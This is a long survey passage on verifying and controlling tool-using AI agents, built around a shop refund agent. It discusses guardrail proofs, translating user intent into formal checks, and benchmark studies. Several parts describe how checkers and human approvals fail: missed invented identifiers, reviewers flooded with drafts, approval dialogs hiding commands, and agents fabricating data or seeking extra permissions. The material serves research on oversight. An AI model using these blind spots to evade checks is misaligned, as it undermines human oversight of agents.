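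Several papers make stronger claims in their titles than in their theorems. *Pandora's Toolbox Or Why Agent Safety Cannot Be Verified* (2026) proves that no algorithm can block all dangerous programs and only those. This does not rule out a guardrail that blocks all dangerous programs and some harmless ones. *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* (2026) proves that no algorithm can list all the statements that hold in every finite system, but acknowledges that exhaustive search can decide safety for any one fixed finite system. The problem is therefore decidable for a system as large as a language model, but the search would take far too long to be practical.

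Melo, Máximo and colleagues (2024) argue in *On the Undecidability of Artificial Intelligence Alignment* that, because nobody can check arbitrary models for alignment after they are built, developers should build guarantees into the architecture, both that the model is aligned and that it always halts.

McCann (2026), in *The Two Boundaries*, proposes a similar solution for actions. The software checks each structured request instead of predicting what the program behind it will do. Checking whether a $40 refund fits under today's limit takes one addition and one comparison, no matter how complicated the program that requested it. McCann concedes that a system with a bad policy will carry out that policy exactly as written.

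#### A further argument from McCann

In *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance*, McCann also uses Rice's theorem to argue that an agent system needs a component whose behaviour the rest of the system can't analyse, such as a language model. This "Necessity Theorem" is one of the paper's results that Rocq has not checked. McCann defines *C* as the property of answering every factual question correctly, applies Rice's theorem to *C*, and concludes that no computable function can replace the component.

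Rice's theorem applies only to properties that at least one computable function has. McCann writes that no computable function has *C*. If so, *C* is trivial, so the theorem doesn't apply, and an algorithm can decide *C* by answering "no" every time.

Even if it did, it would show only that no algorithm can recognise every function with *C*, and such a function could still exist. There is a simpler way to show that none does. If the factual questions include whether any given program stops, Turing's result implies that no computable function answers them all. But McCann notes that language models are computable too, so the result also means that no language model can answer them all, and it gives no reason to think that an opaque component can do what a transparent one can't.

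#### Rice's theorem and ordinary language

*SentinelAgent* (2026) extends the argument to instructions in ordinary language. It concludes that no deterministic algorithm can classify the intent of every delegated task without error, unless people write the tasks in a formal grammar. The paper cites Rice's theorem, but that theorem is about programs, and the paper grants that descriptions in natural language aren't formal programs. There are only finitely many messages of up to 1,000 characters, so in principle a table could hold the right answer for each, if each had one. "Refund the kettle" has no single right answer, because the answer is different for Maya and Tom. *SentinelAgent* also points out that a classifier lacks the agent's internal state and the context of the task. This reason is similar to the two-customers argument and doesn't depend on Rice's theorem.

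### Vassilev's proof about guardrails

In June 2026 the US standards agency, NIST, announced a proof that no finite set of guardrails can withstand every adversarial prompt. Apostol Vassilev, a senior scientist at the agency, published the proof in *IEEE Security & Privacy* in May.

The proof, in Vassilev (2025), in *Robust AI Security and Alignment*, adapts a version of Gödel's incompleteness theorem by Gregory Chaitin. It starts with a policy and the infinite set of prompts that the policy forbids. For a prompt *x* from this set and a number *n*, it considers the statement

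*T*: every program that outputs *x* is longer than *n* bits.

There are only finitely many programs of at most *n* bits, and each outputs at most one prompt, so *T* is true of infinitely many forbidden prompts. Suppose a checker could verify *T* for one of them. A program could then search through all forbidden prompts and all possible proofs until the checker accepted a proof of *T* for some prompt *x*, and then output *x*. This program needs only a fixed amount of code plus about log₂ *n* bits to store *n*, so for large *n* it is much shorter than *n* bits. But the checker has just verified that no program of at most *n* bits outputs *x*. So a checker that accepts only true statements can never verify *T* for large *n*.

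The unprovable statement is about how short a program that prints the prompt can be, not whether the prompt gets past the guardrail. Vassilev defines the set as the prompts that the policy deems unacceptable "and blocks", so by definition the guardrail stops every prompt in the proof. A guardrail that blocks all prompts is a counterexample to the announced conclusion, because it can't verify *T* either, but no adversarial prompt gets through.

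The proof therefore doesn't establish that every guardrail has a hole. But attackers have repeatedly found ways past filters that judge ordinary language, and Vassilev cites a test in which attacks on agents succeeded almost every time. The release advises continually searching for new attacks, updating the guardrails, and limiting the damage when one fails, which makes sense even without the theorem. A control layer limits the damage because the shop's daily limit holds even if a prompt takes over the refund agent.

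### Undecidable, unrecorded and undefined

A question is undecidable only if every case has a definite answer but no algorithm can find all of those answers. The Goldbach program either will or won't perform the forbidden action, even if no one ever finds out which. Pérez-Acle assumes throughout that the gatekeeper knows the rule and can read the code, and so describes the obstruction as "computational, not informational".

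In the kettle case, by contrast, the control layer is missing information about which kettle Tom meant. With that information, it could check the refund in a single comparison. Unlimited computing power wouldn't supply it, but asking Tom would. Asking the owner of the Goldbach program wouldn't help, because the owner doesn't know the answer either.

*Protecting the System, Stranding the User* gives another reason, which it says doesn't rest on Rice's theorem. Intent has no formal definition, so a check has nothing definite to confirm. This reason applies well to a request such as "refund whatever is fair", where even the customer may have no exact amount in mind. It applies less well to the kettle, because Tom had one particular object in mind. A shop could also define "the item the customer meant" as the item the customer selects on a form. A proof could use this definition, but customers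 would still sometimes select the wrong item.

| Question | Obstacle | What would help |
|---|---|---|
| Will an arbitrary program ever pay too much? | No algorithm answers this for every program. | Allow only programs that come with a proof, or check each payment. |
| Which kettle did Tom mean? | The answer exists, but the record doesn't contain it. | Ask Tom. |
| Was the refund fair? | Nobody has fixed what counts as fair. | Somebody has to choose a definition and defend it. |

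In *The Two Boundaries*, McCann makes both kinds of argument about content filters. The paper first cites Rice's theorem to argue that no general method can predict whether a program will ever produce a forbidden output. It then notes that filters avoid this problem by checking one output at a time, but that nobody can formally specify "harmful" or "factually correct" for ordinary language. Only the second argument bears on intent. People who mistake an undefined question for an undecidable one may look for a better algorithm when they need to discuss or decide what the question means.

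### An older dispute about verified programs

Computer scientists debated what program proofs can show long before language models existed. In *Social Processes and Proofs of Theorems and Programs* (1979), Richard De Millo, Richard Lipton and Alan Perlis argued that mathematicians trust a theorem because colleagues read the proof, discuss it, simplify it and use it in their own work. They argued that nobody would do this for proofs about programs, because those proofs were long and dull. They added that people's requirements for a program are informal while the program is formal, so the step from one to the other can't itself be formal.

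Leslie Lamport replied in a letter that year that a theorem either follows from its axioms or doesn't, and that a general election can't settle which. Later experience supports him on this point. Proof assistants now check millions of lines of proof that no person will read, and their mistakes have been few enough to list one by one. But a proof assistant doesn't check whether the formal statement matches the informal request. It accepts a valid proof about the $40 kettle or the $60 kettle, regardless of which one the user meant.

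Brian Cantwell Smith's *The Limits of Correctness* (1985), written for a conference on preventing nuclear war, centres on that step. In October 1960 an American early-warning station in Greenland had reported a massive Soviet missile attack because its radar had picked up the rising moon. Smith argued that a program works with a model of the world, and every model leaves things out. A proof of correctness relates the program to a specification written in terms of the model. It does not show how well the model fits the world, where the program acts. In the shop, the model contains orders, amounts and messages, but not what Tom has in mind.

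James Fetzer's *Program Verification: The Very Idea* (1988) raised a different objection. Fetzer argued that logic can establish conclusions about algorithms and abstract machines, but that a program running on a physical computer is a causal process whose behaviour has to be observed, so no proof can guarantee it. Ten computer scientists, including David Gries and Nancy Leveson, complained in a joint letter in 1989 that Fetzer had attacked a claim nobody in the field made, and they criticised the journal for publishing the article. In a separate reply, John Dobson and Brian Randell pointed out the difference between the field's public image and what its members knew in private.

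Avra Cohn, who worked on the verification of a British microprocessor called Viper, wrote in 1989 that the word "proof" does not properly apply to an intended behaviour or a physical chip. One can prove only that one formal description agrees with another. The chip's promoters had been less careful, and in 1991 a company that had licensed the technology sued the Ministry of Defence over the claim that the design was proved. The company went into liquidation before a court could hear the case.

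Cohn's statement covers both gaps in the refund agent's guarantee. Engineers can narrow the gap between the description and the machine by verifying the compiled file and testing its surroundings. To narrow the gap between the description and the intended behaviour, they need information from the people whose intentions matter.

### Specifying harm with a model of the world

One way to address Smith's criticism is to include more of the world in the theorem. David Dalrymple and colleagues, including Yoshua Bengio, Stuart Russell and Max Tegmark, proposed this in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (2024). In their approach, a world model describes mathematically how an AI system affects its surroundings, and a safety specification describes which effects are acceptable. A verifier produces an auditable proof that the system meets the specification relative to the world model. The proof can also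 be of a bound on a probability, such as less than one chance in a million of a specified harm.

For the refund agent, the world model could assign a probability to each kettle the customer might mean, and the specification could limit the chance of refunding the wrong one. The two-customers argument doesn't rule out a proof that the agent meets this limit, because the proof would cover whole situations and not only records. But the argument does restrict how low the limit can be. If the model assigns a 30% probability to the customer meaning the $60 kettle, no verifier can correctly certify an error rate below 30% for an agent that pays without asking.

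The shop would also have to estimate the 30% itself, perhaps from past complaints, because the proof can't supply it. If the true figure among its customers is 45%, the theorem is still true of the model, but the shop will refund the wrong kettle much more often than the certificate allows.

The proposal looks most promising where people agree on what counts as harm and science can predict it. A specification for a chemical plant can set a maximum pressure without covering everything people value, and engineers have good equations for pressure. The proposal is harder to apply to customers' wishes, because no comparable equations exist for what customers mean by their words.

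In the 2024 essay *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Andrew Dickson doubted that the approach would work for the most serious dangers. Dickson argued that proofs are about symbols, and that nobody has models of biology or human behaviour accurate enough to support strong guarantees. Even a good model would need detailed, current data about the situation. Nora Ammann, one of Dalrymple's co-authors, answered critics in January 2025. Supporters of the approach point out that it offers guarantees relative to a stated model, with explicit uncertainty, rather than certainty about the world. This answers the charge of overclaiming but leaves open whether anyone can build the models.

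The control layers of 2026 have avoided this problem by using small models of the world. In the transfer experiment by Wu and colleagues, the state consists of the money sent so far, the limit and the agent's level of privilege. They acknowledge that their verifier shows only that no written axiom is broken. If the people writing the axioms forget an important one, the agent can comply and still cause harm. McCann, who also builds such systems, writes that deciding whether a policy is right requires human judgment.

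The critics also limit their claims. *Protecting the System, Stranding the User* accepts that software outside the model can enforce budgets and permissions, and doesn't call that design wrong. Its main criticism is that the design protects the system but leaves the user to deal with the consequences when something fails. Pérez-Acle rejects the idea that gatekeeping is hopeless and advises people who write rules to require, where possible, something that an observer can see the program do, such as publishing a signed statement before it acts. For the shop, such a rule would require the customer to confirm the item before the agent pays.

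## Turning a request into something that can be checked

Before a customer can confirm a refund, software has to turn the customer's message into a specific proposal, such as "refund the $60 kettle". Lahiri calls this intent formalization, the translation of what a user informally wants into formal statements that a program can check. The software translates the request, tests the translation, and asks the user about cases where plausible readings differ. The control layer then enforces the reading the user chose. The shop's owner goes through this once for each rule, and a customer may have to do so whenever a message is unclear.

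Lahiri writes about code written by AI. If a user asks for a program that removes duplicates from the list 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, a model will typically write one that returns 1, 2, 3, 4. The user may have wanted 1, 3, 4, which leaves out every number that appears more than once, and a program that returns either list would run without an error.

### From a single test to a full specification

Formal statements differ in how much they settle. Lahiri describes a range with four levels, illustrated here with the owner's $1,000 limit.

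| Level | Example | How software uses it |
|---|---|---|
| Test | After paying $940, the control layer refuses $61. | Runs the program on this case |
| Code contract | Today's payments total at most $1,000. | Checks the condition while the program runs |
| Logical contract | The same condition holds in every state the program can reach. | Proves it before the program runs |
| Domain-specific language | A complete description of the refund rules in a specialised notation | Generates the program from it |

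The owner can judge a test at a glance but may not be able to read a logical contract. Lahiri therefore suggests starting with tests for the points people are most likely to misunderstand, and adding stronger specifications where mistakes would be serious.

Work at the most complete level has already produced working software. In the 3DGen project, AI agents translated the written standards for 20 network message formats into a specialised language, and a compiler turned the results into verified parsers. Engineers write such standards to be precise, but most letters to a shop are not written that way.

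### Testing a specification before there is a program

Lahiri measures a specification against a set *T* of tests, each consisting of an input *i* and its correct output *o*. A specification *S* is sound for *T* if it accepts every correct output:

*S*(*i*, *o*) holds for every (*i*, *o*) in *T*.

This is the reverse of schema soundness, which requires a check to accept only valid messages. Here, a sound specification never rejects a right answer. Completeness measures whether it rejects wrong ones. The tester alters each correct output and calculates

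completeness = altered outputs that *S* rejects ÷ all altered outputs.

Neither measure needs a finished program. Lahiri applied them to a specification that GPT-4 had written in Dafny for a program that finds the common elements of two lists, *a* and *b*. Expert reviewers had labelled it "strong". It has two conditions:

- for every *x*, *x* ∈ *result* ⇒ *x* ∈ *a* and *x* ∈ *b*;
- no element appears twice in *result*.

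If *a* is [1, 2, 3] and *b* is [2, 3, 4], the correct result is [2, 3], which satisfies both conditions. The specification is therefore sound for this test. Here are four altered results:

| Altered result | Original specification | With ⇔ in place of ⇒ |
|---|---|---|
| [2, 3, 4] | Rejects it, because 4 is not in *a* | Rejects it |
| [2, 2, 3] | Rejects it, because 2 appears twice | Rejects it |
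| [2] | Accepts it | Rejects it, because 3 is missing |
| [ ] | Accepts it | Rejects it, because 2 and 3 are missing |

The original requires everything in the result to be a common element, but it doesn't require every common element to be in the result. An empty list meets both conditions because it has no elements to break them, so Dafny could verify a program that always returns an empty list. The empty list of tool calls made a rule vacuous in a similar way in Moon and Varshney's experiment. Replacing the implication with an equivalence raises completeness on these four alterations from 50% to 100%.

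The corrected specification also accepts [3, 2]. If order doesn't matter, it is right to do so, because the altered output is also a correct answer. This is partly why Lahiri reports completeness as a fraction. The measure also depends on choosing alterations that resemble mistakes people and models make.

Across the evaluation, the automated measures exposed three specifications that people had labelled wrongly and two that copying errors had made inconsistent. But the measures rely on correct outputs that somebody has to supply. Suppose a user wants repeated elements kept, so that [1, 2, 2] and [2, 2, 3] give [2, 2]. The condition against duplicates rejects that answer, so whether the specification is sound depends on what the user wants.

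*Neuro-Formal Verification* (2026) describes a workflow that begins with these measures and ends with a machine-checked proof about a model of the program. Along the way, the user can review the specification and tests and point out mistakes. The paper calls the result "formal program reasoning" rather than end-to-end verification, because no proof covers all the translations.

### Asking about the cases that separate the readings

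TiCoder, a system from Lahiri's group, relies on the user to identify correct outputs. It uses a language model to generate several candidate programs and looks for inputs on which their outputs differ. It then shows the user one such input with a possible output, and the user answers yes, no or undefined. TiCoder discards the candidates that conflict with the answer.

Suppose the request is for a program that finds the shared elements of two lists. The user approves [2, 3] as the output for [1, 2, 3] and [2, 3, 4]. TiCoder then shows [2, 2] as a possible output for [1, 2, 2] and [2, 2, 3], and the user rejects it. This rules out every candidate program that keeps duplicates, and the user hasn't had to read any code.

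Fakhoury, Naik and colleagues published the user study in *IEEE Transactions on Software Engineering* in 2024. It asked 15 professional developers to judge whether AI-written code did what the task required. According to Lahiri, they were right in 40% of cases without TiCoder and 84% with it, and reported a lower mental load when using it. The study was small, the tasks came from programming benchmarks, and the participants were used to thinking in examples. Customers might do worse, although "which kettle?" is also an easier question.

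The same method can settle whether the owner's $1,000 limit applies to a calendar day or to any 24-hour period. The owner can be asked whether the agent may pay $1,000 just before midnight and again just after. If the owner says no, the calendar-day reading is wrong. A test in which the agent has already paid $940 that day and gets a request for $61 doesn't help, because the payment would exceed the limit under both readings.

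Well-chosen yes-or-no questions can narrow the possible readings quickly. If each answer rules out half of them, about log₂ *n* questions are enough for *n* readings, or three for eight. One question is enough for the two kettles. If 2% of customers pick the wrong kettle when asked, asking cuts the error rate in the earlier example from at least 30% to 2%.

This method can fail to produce a question when one is needed. Suppose the agent translates Tom's message ten times and chooses the $40 kettle each time because it comes first in the order. TiCoder's approach would not produce a question because the candidates agree, but a model can give consistent translations of a message that has two meanings. A shop can partly address this with ordinary code that counts the items in the order matching the word "kettle" and requires a question if there is more than one.

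### How often translations are wrong

Researchers have measured translation most thoroughly for the Planning Domain Definition Language (PDDL). A PDDL problem lists objects, their starting state and a goal, and a program called a planner searches for actions that reach the goal. If a user wants the red block on top of the blue one and the translation has them the other way round, the planner will still find a plan, but for the wrong goal.

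Dantas and colleagues call specification the bottleneck for safe agents, and cite a benchmark in which only 24.8% to 34.2% of translations were correct in meaning. Both figures come from *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024), which converted each translation and its reference into a graph of objects and facts, then checked whether the graphs were the same apart from the objects' names. A planner could solve 94.4% of the problems that GPT-4o wrote, but only 24.8% had the right meaning. The 34.2% figure is for a smaller model, Gemma 2 27B, after training on the task.

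Those numbers are out of date, and they measured more than misunderstanding. Many of the errors came from models adding object types that the given version of PDDL didn't use, and accuracy rose considerably when the researchers ignored these errors. Rosa, Santos and colleagues (2026), in *Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation*, tested newer models on about 60 problems from the same benchmark. Each model could revise its translation twice after feedback from automatic checks and a language model acting as critic.

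| Model | Study | Correct at first | Correct after feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | Zuo and colleagues | 24.8% | Not tried |
| Gemma 2 27B, trained on the task | Zuo and colleagues | 34.2% | Not tried |
| GPT-4.1-mini | Rosa and colleagues | 18.3% | 26.7% |
| GPT-5.5 | Rosa and colleagues | 93.2% | 93.2% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | Rosa and colleagues | 96.7% | 100% |

GPT-5.5 reached 98.3% when the instructions included a worked example. So in two years, translations of clear descriptions of simple problems have gone from mostly wrong to nearly always right.

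The checks improved less convincingly. With GPT-5.5 and no worked example, they accepted all 59 completed translations, including four with the wrong meaning. Rosa and colleagues also inspected by hand 24 outputs from the GPT-4.1-mini runs. The critic's verdict matched theirs on only 13. It had accepted three unfaithful translations and rejected eight faithful ones. Bad feedback can also spoil a good translation. On one set of 60 problems, the share of GPT-4.1-mini's translations that matched the reference fell from 66.7% to 56.7% after feedback.

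Problems involving time and quantities are harder to assess. On these problems, the two stronger models passed the automatic checks in at least 93% of cases but matched the reference in only 7% to 25%. A match required the same facts, numbers and quantity to optimise as the reference, so some mismatches may have been valid alternatives.

Benchmark descriptions are also more precise than ordinary requests. For *Which LLM is Best for Translating Natural Language Goals to PDDL*, Balyo, Chrpa and Youngblood (2026) collected 90 goals from employees of their company, more than half of them written by people who had never used PDDL. The given vocabulary could express only 45 of the goals, and the models should have declined the rest. Six models from 2025 responded correctly in 92% to 96% of cases, but each wrote a formal goal for two to four of the 45 that could not be expressed. They had done this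 more often before the researchers added examples of inexpressible goals to the instructions.

In the shop, a customer might ask for a refund "if that seems fair". If the only available action is a refund of a fixed amount, a model that always produces a formal request will leave out the condition, and the control layer will never receive it.

### A model translates and a solver judges

AWS sells a service called Automated Reasoning checks that, like Greenlight, uses a model to translate and formal logic to judge. According to AWS's *What are Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails?*, a company uploads a document containing its rules, and the service extracts logical rules and a list of variables. People review and test the result. When a chatbot later answers a question, the service uses language models to translate the exchange into values for the variables, then uses formal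 logic to determine whether the answer agrees with the rules.

Suppose the shop gives a refund exactly when an item is damaged, arrived within the last 30 days and wasn't on sale. A customer writes that a kettle came two weeks ago with a cracked lid, and the agent replies that a refund is due. The translation records damage, 14 days and a refund, but not whether the kettle was on sale, so the reply is consistent with the rules but doesn't follow from them. The service can point out this missing assumption, which a person might overlook. But if the model had recorded 40 days instead of 14, the service would have applied the rules correctly to the wrong number and found that the reply contradicted them.

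A verdict of "valid" applies only to what the variables capture. AWS gives the example of a student who uses a fake doctor's note to claim the right to hand in homework late. The service may find the claim valid if no variable records whether the note is genuine.

AWS's *Automated Reasoning policies now include references to the source document* (2026) advertises "up to 99% accuracy at detecting correct responses". This is a best result, and it depends on the models choosing the right values and on the extracted rules matching the company's. "Correct" means correct according to the extracted rules. The figure doesn't measure how many wrong responses get through. A checker could recognise 99 of 100 correct responses and still pass 20 of 100 wrong ones. The service only reports its findings, so the shop's own software would have to stop a payment.

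Reviewers must still judge whether the extracted rules match what the company means. The source references help by linking each rule to the passage it came from. AWS's *Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails add new policy refinement workflows* (2026) describes two further aids. One changes the rules until they pass tests written in ordinary language, so the rules can be no better than the tests. The other rewrites the descriptions of variables to make ambiguous translations rarer. This is useful when the descriptions were vague, but a request like "refund the kettle" is itself ambiguous and should still be flagged as such.

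The European edition of AWS's *What are Automated Reasoning checks in Amazon Bedrock Guardrails?* mentions that several models do the translation. Comparing their translations exposes a mistake only if the models don't all make the same one. If two models each misread 5% of messages, independently of each other, both misread the same message in 0.25% of cases. If they misread the same messages in the same way, both are wrong in 5% of cases and the comparison exposes none of these errors. Models trained on similar text may well both pick the first kettle. When the translations disagree, a person still has to choose between them.

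### A formal language that the user can read

Another approach is to show the user the translation of their request, a formal query written in a language close enough to English to read. *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts* (Councilman, Fu and colleagues, 2025) describes Astrogator, a system that does this for Ansible, a language for setting up computers. Once the user confirms the query, a verifier checks the AI-written program against it.

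Let *U* be the set of programs that would satisfy the user and ⟦*s*⟧ the set of programs that satisfy the query *s*. No software can test whether a program is in *U*, and the user may not be able to read Ansible. The verifier can test whether it is in ⟦*s*⟧. A good query shouldn't exclude anything the user would accept, so

*U* ⊆ ⟦*s*⟧.

The programs that satisfy a formal query will often differ from the programs that do what the user meant. A request to create a file at a certain place doesn't specify the file's contents or owner, so a program can satisfy the query and still give the file to the wrong owner.

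On 21 programming tasks, Astrogator verified 83% of the correct programs and identified 92% of the incorrect ones. It can catch errors that are hard to see in the code. For example, some programs were supposed to replace the line in a settings file that began with `key=`, but searched for lines beginning with `key`, so they could also overwrite a different setting called `keys`. The user doesn't have to notice this error, but still has to check that the query names the right setting.

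The shop could have a tiny language of this sort, with sentences such as "Refund the steel kettle, $60, to the card used for the order." Ordinary code would produce the sentence from the same record that goes to the payment service, so the two can't differ. If a model wrote the sentence separately, the customer might approve $60 while the record contained $40.

### Answers derived from recorded evidence

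An agent also makes factual claims, such as "this order has already had one refund". *Evidence-Grounded Verified Agentic Reasoning* (Ren, 2026) has the model prove such answers in Lean. The model first turns the question into a formal goal with a blank for the answer. It then calls tools that read a table, and the surrounding software records each result as evidence. The model can't create evidence itself. It then proposes an answer with a proof. If Lean rejects the proof, the model can try again, and if it never succeeds, the system declines to answer.

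With formal goals prepared in advance, the system answered all 120 questions correctly, while the same model with the same tools but no proofs answered 114 correctly. Ren also altered some tables to contradict facts that the model had learned in training. The proof system followed the altered table in every case, while the model with tools alone followed it in 16 of 20 cases with large changes and 18 of 20 with small ones.

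When the model also had to write the formal goals, Claude Sonnet's accuracy fell to 84.2% and Claude Opus's to 87.5%. Ren attributes four of Sonnet's failures (3.3% of questions) and two of Opus's (1.7%) to a goal that didn't match what the question meant. Most of the other failures came from ambiguous questions or runs that ended without an answer.

Ren's theorems do not cover whether the goal matches the question or what the table means. If a column is labeled "delivered", somebody has to decide whether it holds the date a parcel left the warehouse or the date it arrived. A wrong choice could make a late refund look on time in every proof that uses the column.

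### Letting a guess only remove permissions

A more cautious design doesn't rely on the translation to grant anything. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, use a model's reading of the request only to take permissions away. Let Static be the actions that the owner permits the agent in general, and Guess(*u*) the actions that the request *u* appears to need. The control layer allows

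Allowed(*u*) = Static ∩ Guess(*u*),

which lies within Static whatever the guess. If a user asks for a summary of this month's records, the agent loses access to the tool for exporting the whole database, even though it may use that tool for other tasks. If a user asks for an entry of 23.50, the control layer refuses one of 2,350.

A wrong guess can block useful work but can't add permissions, because the guess only adds prohibitions. It can still let through a wrong action that the owner permits. If the model wrongly identifies Tom's item as the $40 kettle, the control layer will allow the wrong refund and block the right one. Zhu and Wang therefore promise that the agent stays within the user's request only on the condition that the guess is faithful and the control layer has correct information about what each action will do.

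In 306 trials on artificial tasks, no unsafe action took effect, but the system accepted unsafe proposals as drafts for later review at rates between 9% and 27%. Safety therefore depended on whoever reviewed the drafts. A stricter procedure removed the unsafe drafts, but the system then completed substantially less work.

The owner's permissions must remain the upper limit for another reason. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (2026) points out that a customer-service agent serves many people with different aims, so a user's intent should not determine that user's permissions. A customer who dropped a kettle may want a refund, and the shop may want the agent to refuse even if it understands the request correctly.

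### Whether people check what they confirm

A user can't list every permission in advance, because new subtasks come up while an agent works. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) concludes that software must either infer what the user wants or let people state it through policies and approvals. Approval requests protect users only if users read them, and the evidence on whether they do is limited and mostly indirect.

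The TiCoder study gives the clearest figures. Even with concrete examples to judge, professional developers were still wrong about one time in six.

People do turn proposals down. Councilman and colleagues cite a study of an Ansible assistant whose users initially accepted 66% of its suggestions and kept 60% of those unchanged, or about 40% of the total. These figures don't show whether the code they kept was right. *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) found that users became significantly less willing to grant permissions after an agent made a mistake. This caution can't prevent the first mistake, and users who don't notice a mistake may never become more cautious.

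The study suggests letting software decide the cases it can predict confidently and asking the user only about the uncertain ones. With fewer questions, people should be able to give each one more attention, but a confident prediction can be wrong, as with the ten identical translations of Tom's message. Zhu and Wang also list the threat of an attacker who exploits tired reviewers by flooding them with plausible drafts. Reviewers cannot check what the screen leaves out, as when approval dialogs hid part of a command from users of coding agents.

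None of these studies measured how often customers read a confirmation before pressing "yes", so the 2% error rate used above is an assumption. The rate probably depends on how the shop asks the question. Tom can press "yes" out of habit if the shop asks, "Refund the $40 kettle?", but he has to choose one if it shows him both kettles with their prices and neither selected.

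## Measuring what the proofs leave open

The shop can prove that the agent stays within its limit of $1,000 a day, but it has to measure how often customers get the refund they meant. The number of forbidden requests that the control layer blocks is a poor measure of this, because it rises when the agent misbehaves more often and doesn't show whether anybody got a refund. It is the easiest number to collect, since it is already in the logs.

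### The safe success rate

The safe success rate is the share of tasks that an agent completes correctly without breaking a rule. For *n* tasks, let *Rᵢ* be 1 if the agent completed task *i* correctly and 0 otherwise, and let *Vᵢ* be 1 if it broke at least one rule along the way. Then

safe success rate = (1/*n*) Σ *Rᵢ*(1 − *Vᵢ*).

Here are three invented refund agents with 100 tasks each:

| | Agent A | Agent B | Agent C, whose control layer refuses everything |
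|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden requests | 200 | 10 | 50 |
| Blocked | 190 (95%) | 5 (50%) | 50 (100%) |
| Tasks completed correctly | 30 | 90 | 0 |
| Of those, with a broken rule | 8 | 4 | 0 |
| Safe success rate | 22% | 86% | 0% |

Ranked by the share of requests blocked, B comes last, although it serves customers far better than the other two.

A rule that the control layer provably enforces should never be broken, so a recorded violation means that one of the proof's assumptions has failed. The shop learns most from the safe success rate about rules that no theorem covers and about whether results were correct. To check correctness, somebody has to supply the right answer. Benchmark designers write one for each task, but the shop would have to ask its customers, because its database shows a $40 refund to Tom as a success even if it was the wrong refund.

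### A checker that blocked 94% of unsafe actions

In *The Verifier Tax*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) measured safe success on τ-bench, a customer-service benchmark. They ran 50 airline tasks and 115 retail tasks three times each for every combination of two open models and three designs, or 2,970 runs in total. In the first design, every tool call took effect immediately. The second added a planning step and a checker that reviewed each action before it took effect. The third also gave the checker the company's written rules. The checker was the same language model with a different prompt, so nothing about it was proved. After three rejections in a row, the software let the action through.

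A script then searched the logs for broken rules, such as changing an order before verifying the customer's identity, acting without the customer's confirmation, or using invented data. With GPT-OSS-20B on the retail tasks, the checker intercepted 94.1% of forbidden proposals. Yet the safe success rate was below 5% in 11 of the 12 settings. The table shows the share of tasks completed, with the safe success rate in brackets.

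| Model and tasks | Plain agent | With planner and checker | Checker also has the rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% (0.0%) | 25.3% (0.7%) | 23.3% (0.0%) |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% (0.0%) | 20.0% (0.0%) | 21.5% (0.6%) |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% (0.7%) | 26.0% (5.3%) | 25.3% (4.7%) |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% (2.6%) | 5.5% (4.4%) | 5.5% (2.9%) |

According to Sah and colleagues, the rates are low because the model fails to find a permitted way to finish after the checker detects a violation. The most common violation was an invented identifier. In one retail run of the plain agent, a customer didn't want to share personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345. The tool accepted this, and the benchmark counted the task as a success. The script found invented data in 93.7% of GPT-OSS-20B's retail runs.

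That explanation is probably incomplete. The software overrode the checker in only 28 runs, far too few to explain so many violations, so the checker probably missed most of the invented identifiers. The researchers note that a checker that only reads text can't easily tell where an identifier came from. They propose an ordinary program that rejects any identifier not returned by an earlier tool call. The shop already has something similar in its schema, which lists only the customer's own orders.

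The table doesn't show that checking reduces safe completions, though the name "verifier tax" implies it. The plain agents were no safer, and GLM-4-9B's safe success on airline tasks rose with a checker. The checked designs clearly needed more computation, using 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens. Both models are small by current standards and completed fewer than 30% of tasks, even counting those with violations, so the percentages are weak evidence about today's best agents.

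Dantas and colleagues rate the evidence for the verifier tax "Very Low", their lowest rating, which means that the true figures are likely to differ substantially from those reported. They chose this rating because the study has limitations, its simulated setting is narrow, and they had found no independent replication when they last searched on 30 August 2026. They cite two other benchmarks with a similar pattern. In one, the best agent completed fewer than 40% of tasks while respecting every safety constraint. In the other, an agent designed for safety considerably narrowed the gap. Their wording of the claim, "Enforcement reduces SSR", goes further than the original results.

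### Where checks helped

Blocking an action can also help an agent finish its task. *Controller-Agnostic Runtime Safety Certificates for Tool-Using AI Agents via Data-Driven Robust Reachability* (Baheri and Wei, 2026) reports a test of a filter placed between small language models and a simulated file system. The task was to change a file after getting confirmation. One model with 3 billion parameters usually tried to raise its own permissions first. When the filter blocked that call and the software prompted the model again, it got the confirmation. Its success rate rose from 3.3% to 38.7%, and its unsafe outcomes fell from 78.7% to zero. A larger model succeeded in 55.3% of runs with or without the filter, and a smaller one never succeeded. The filter therefore helped a model finish only when the model could find the permitted way to do the task after a refusal.

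Afoud and Wu (2026), in *VReAct*, report a pilot with an agent that answers questions by searching a set of paragraphs. Ordinary code rejected answers that were missing, had the wrong type or came from a tool error. The pilot used an 8-billion-parameter model and ran five questions twice each, with and without these checks. The agent without checks answered none of the ten, while the agent with checks answered eight correctly and declined the other two.

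This evidence is weaker than it looks. The checked agent's repeat runs were identical, so they add nothing to its result of four questions answered out of five. Its software also stopped it from repeating the same search, while the plain agent got stuck repeating searches when it had no step limit. Afoud and Wu say they can't separate the effect of this simple loop control from that of the checks, and they claim no formal guarantee. Adding a planner to the checked agent reduced its score to one in ten. In one case, an early step returned the wrong person, and every later answer passed its own check even though the chain as a whole was wrong.

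*Lean4Agent* (Wang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) examines an agent's written workflow before it is run. Each step has conditions that must hold before it starts and conditions that it should establish. Lean checks that every step's requirements follow from what earlier steps establish. For example, a step that tests a repair needs the details of that repair, and the workflow fails the check if no earlier step passes them on. The proof assumes that the model can do each step correctly when its requirements are met.

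On each of two benchmarks, the researchers compared three workflows that passed with three that failed, using five models. On 50 hard programming problems, agents with passing workflows solved 58.3% and agents with failing ones solved 43.5%. On 100 questions about AI papers, the figures were 36.6% and 27.5%.

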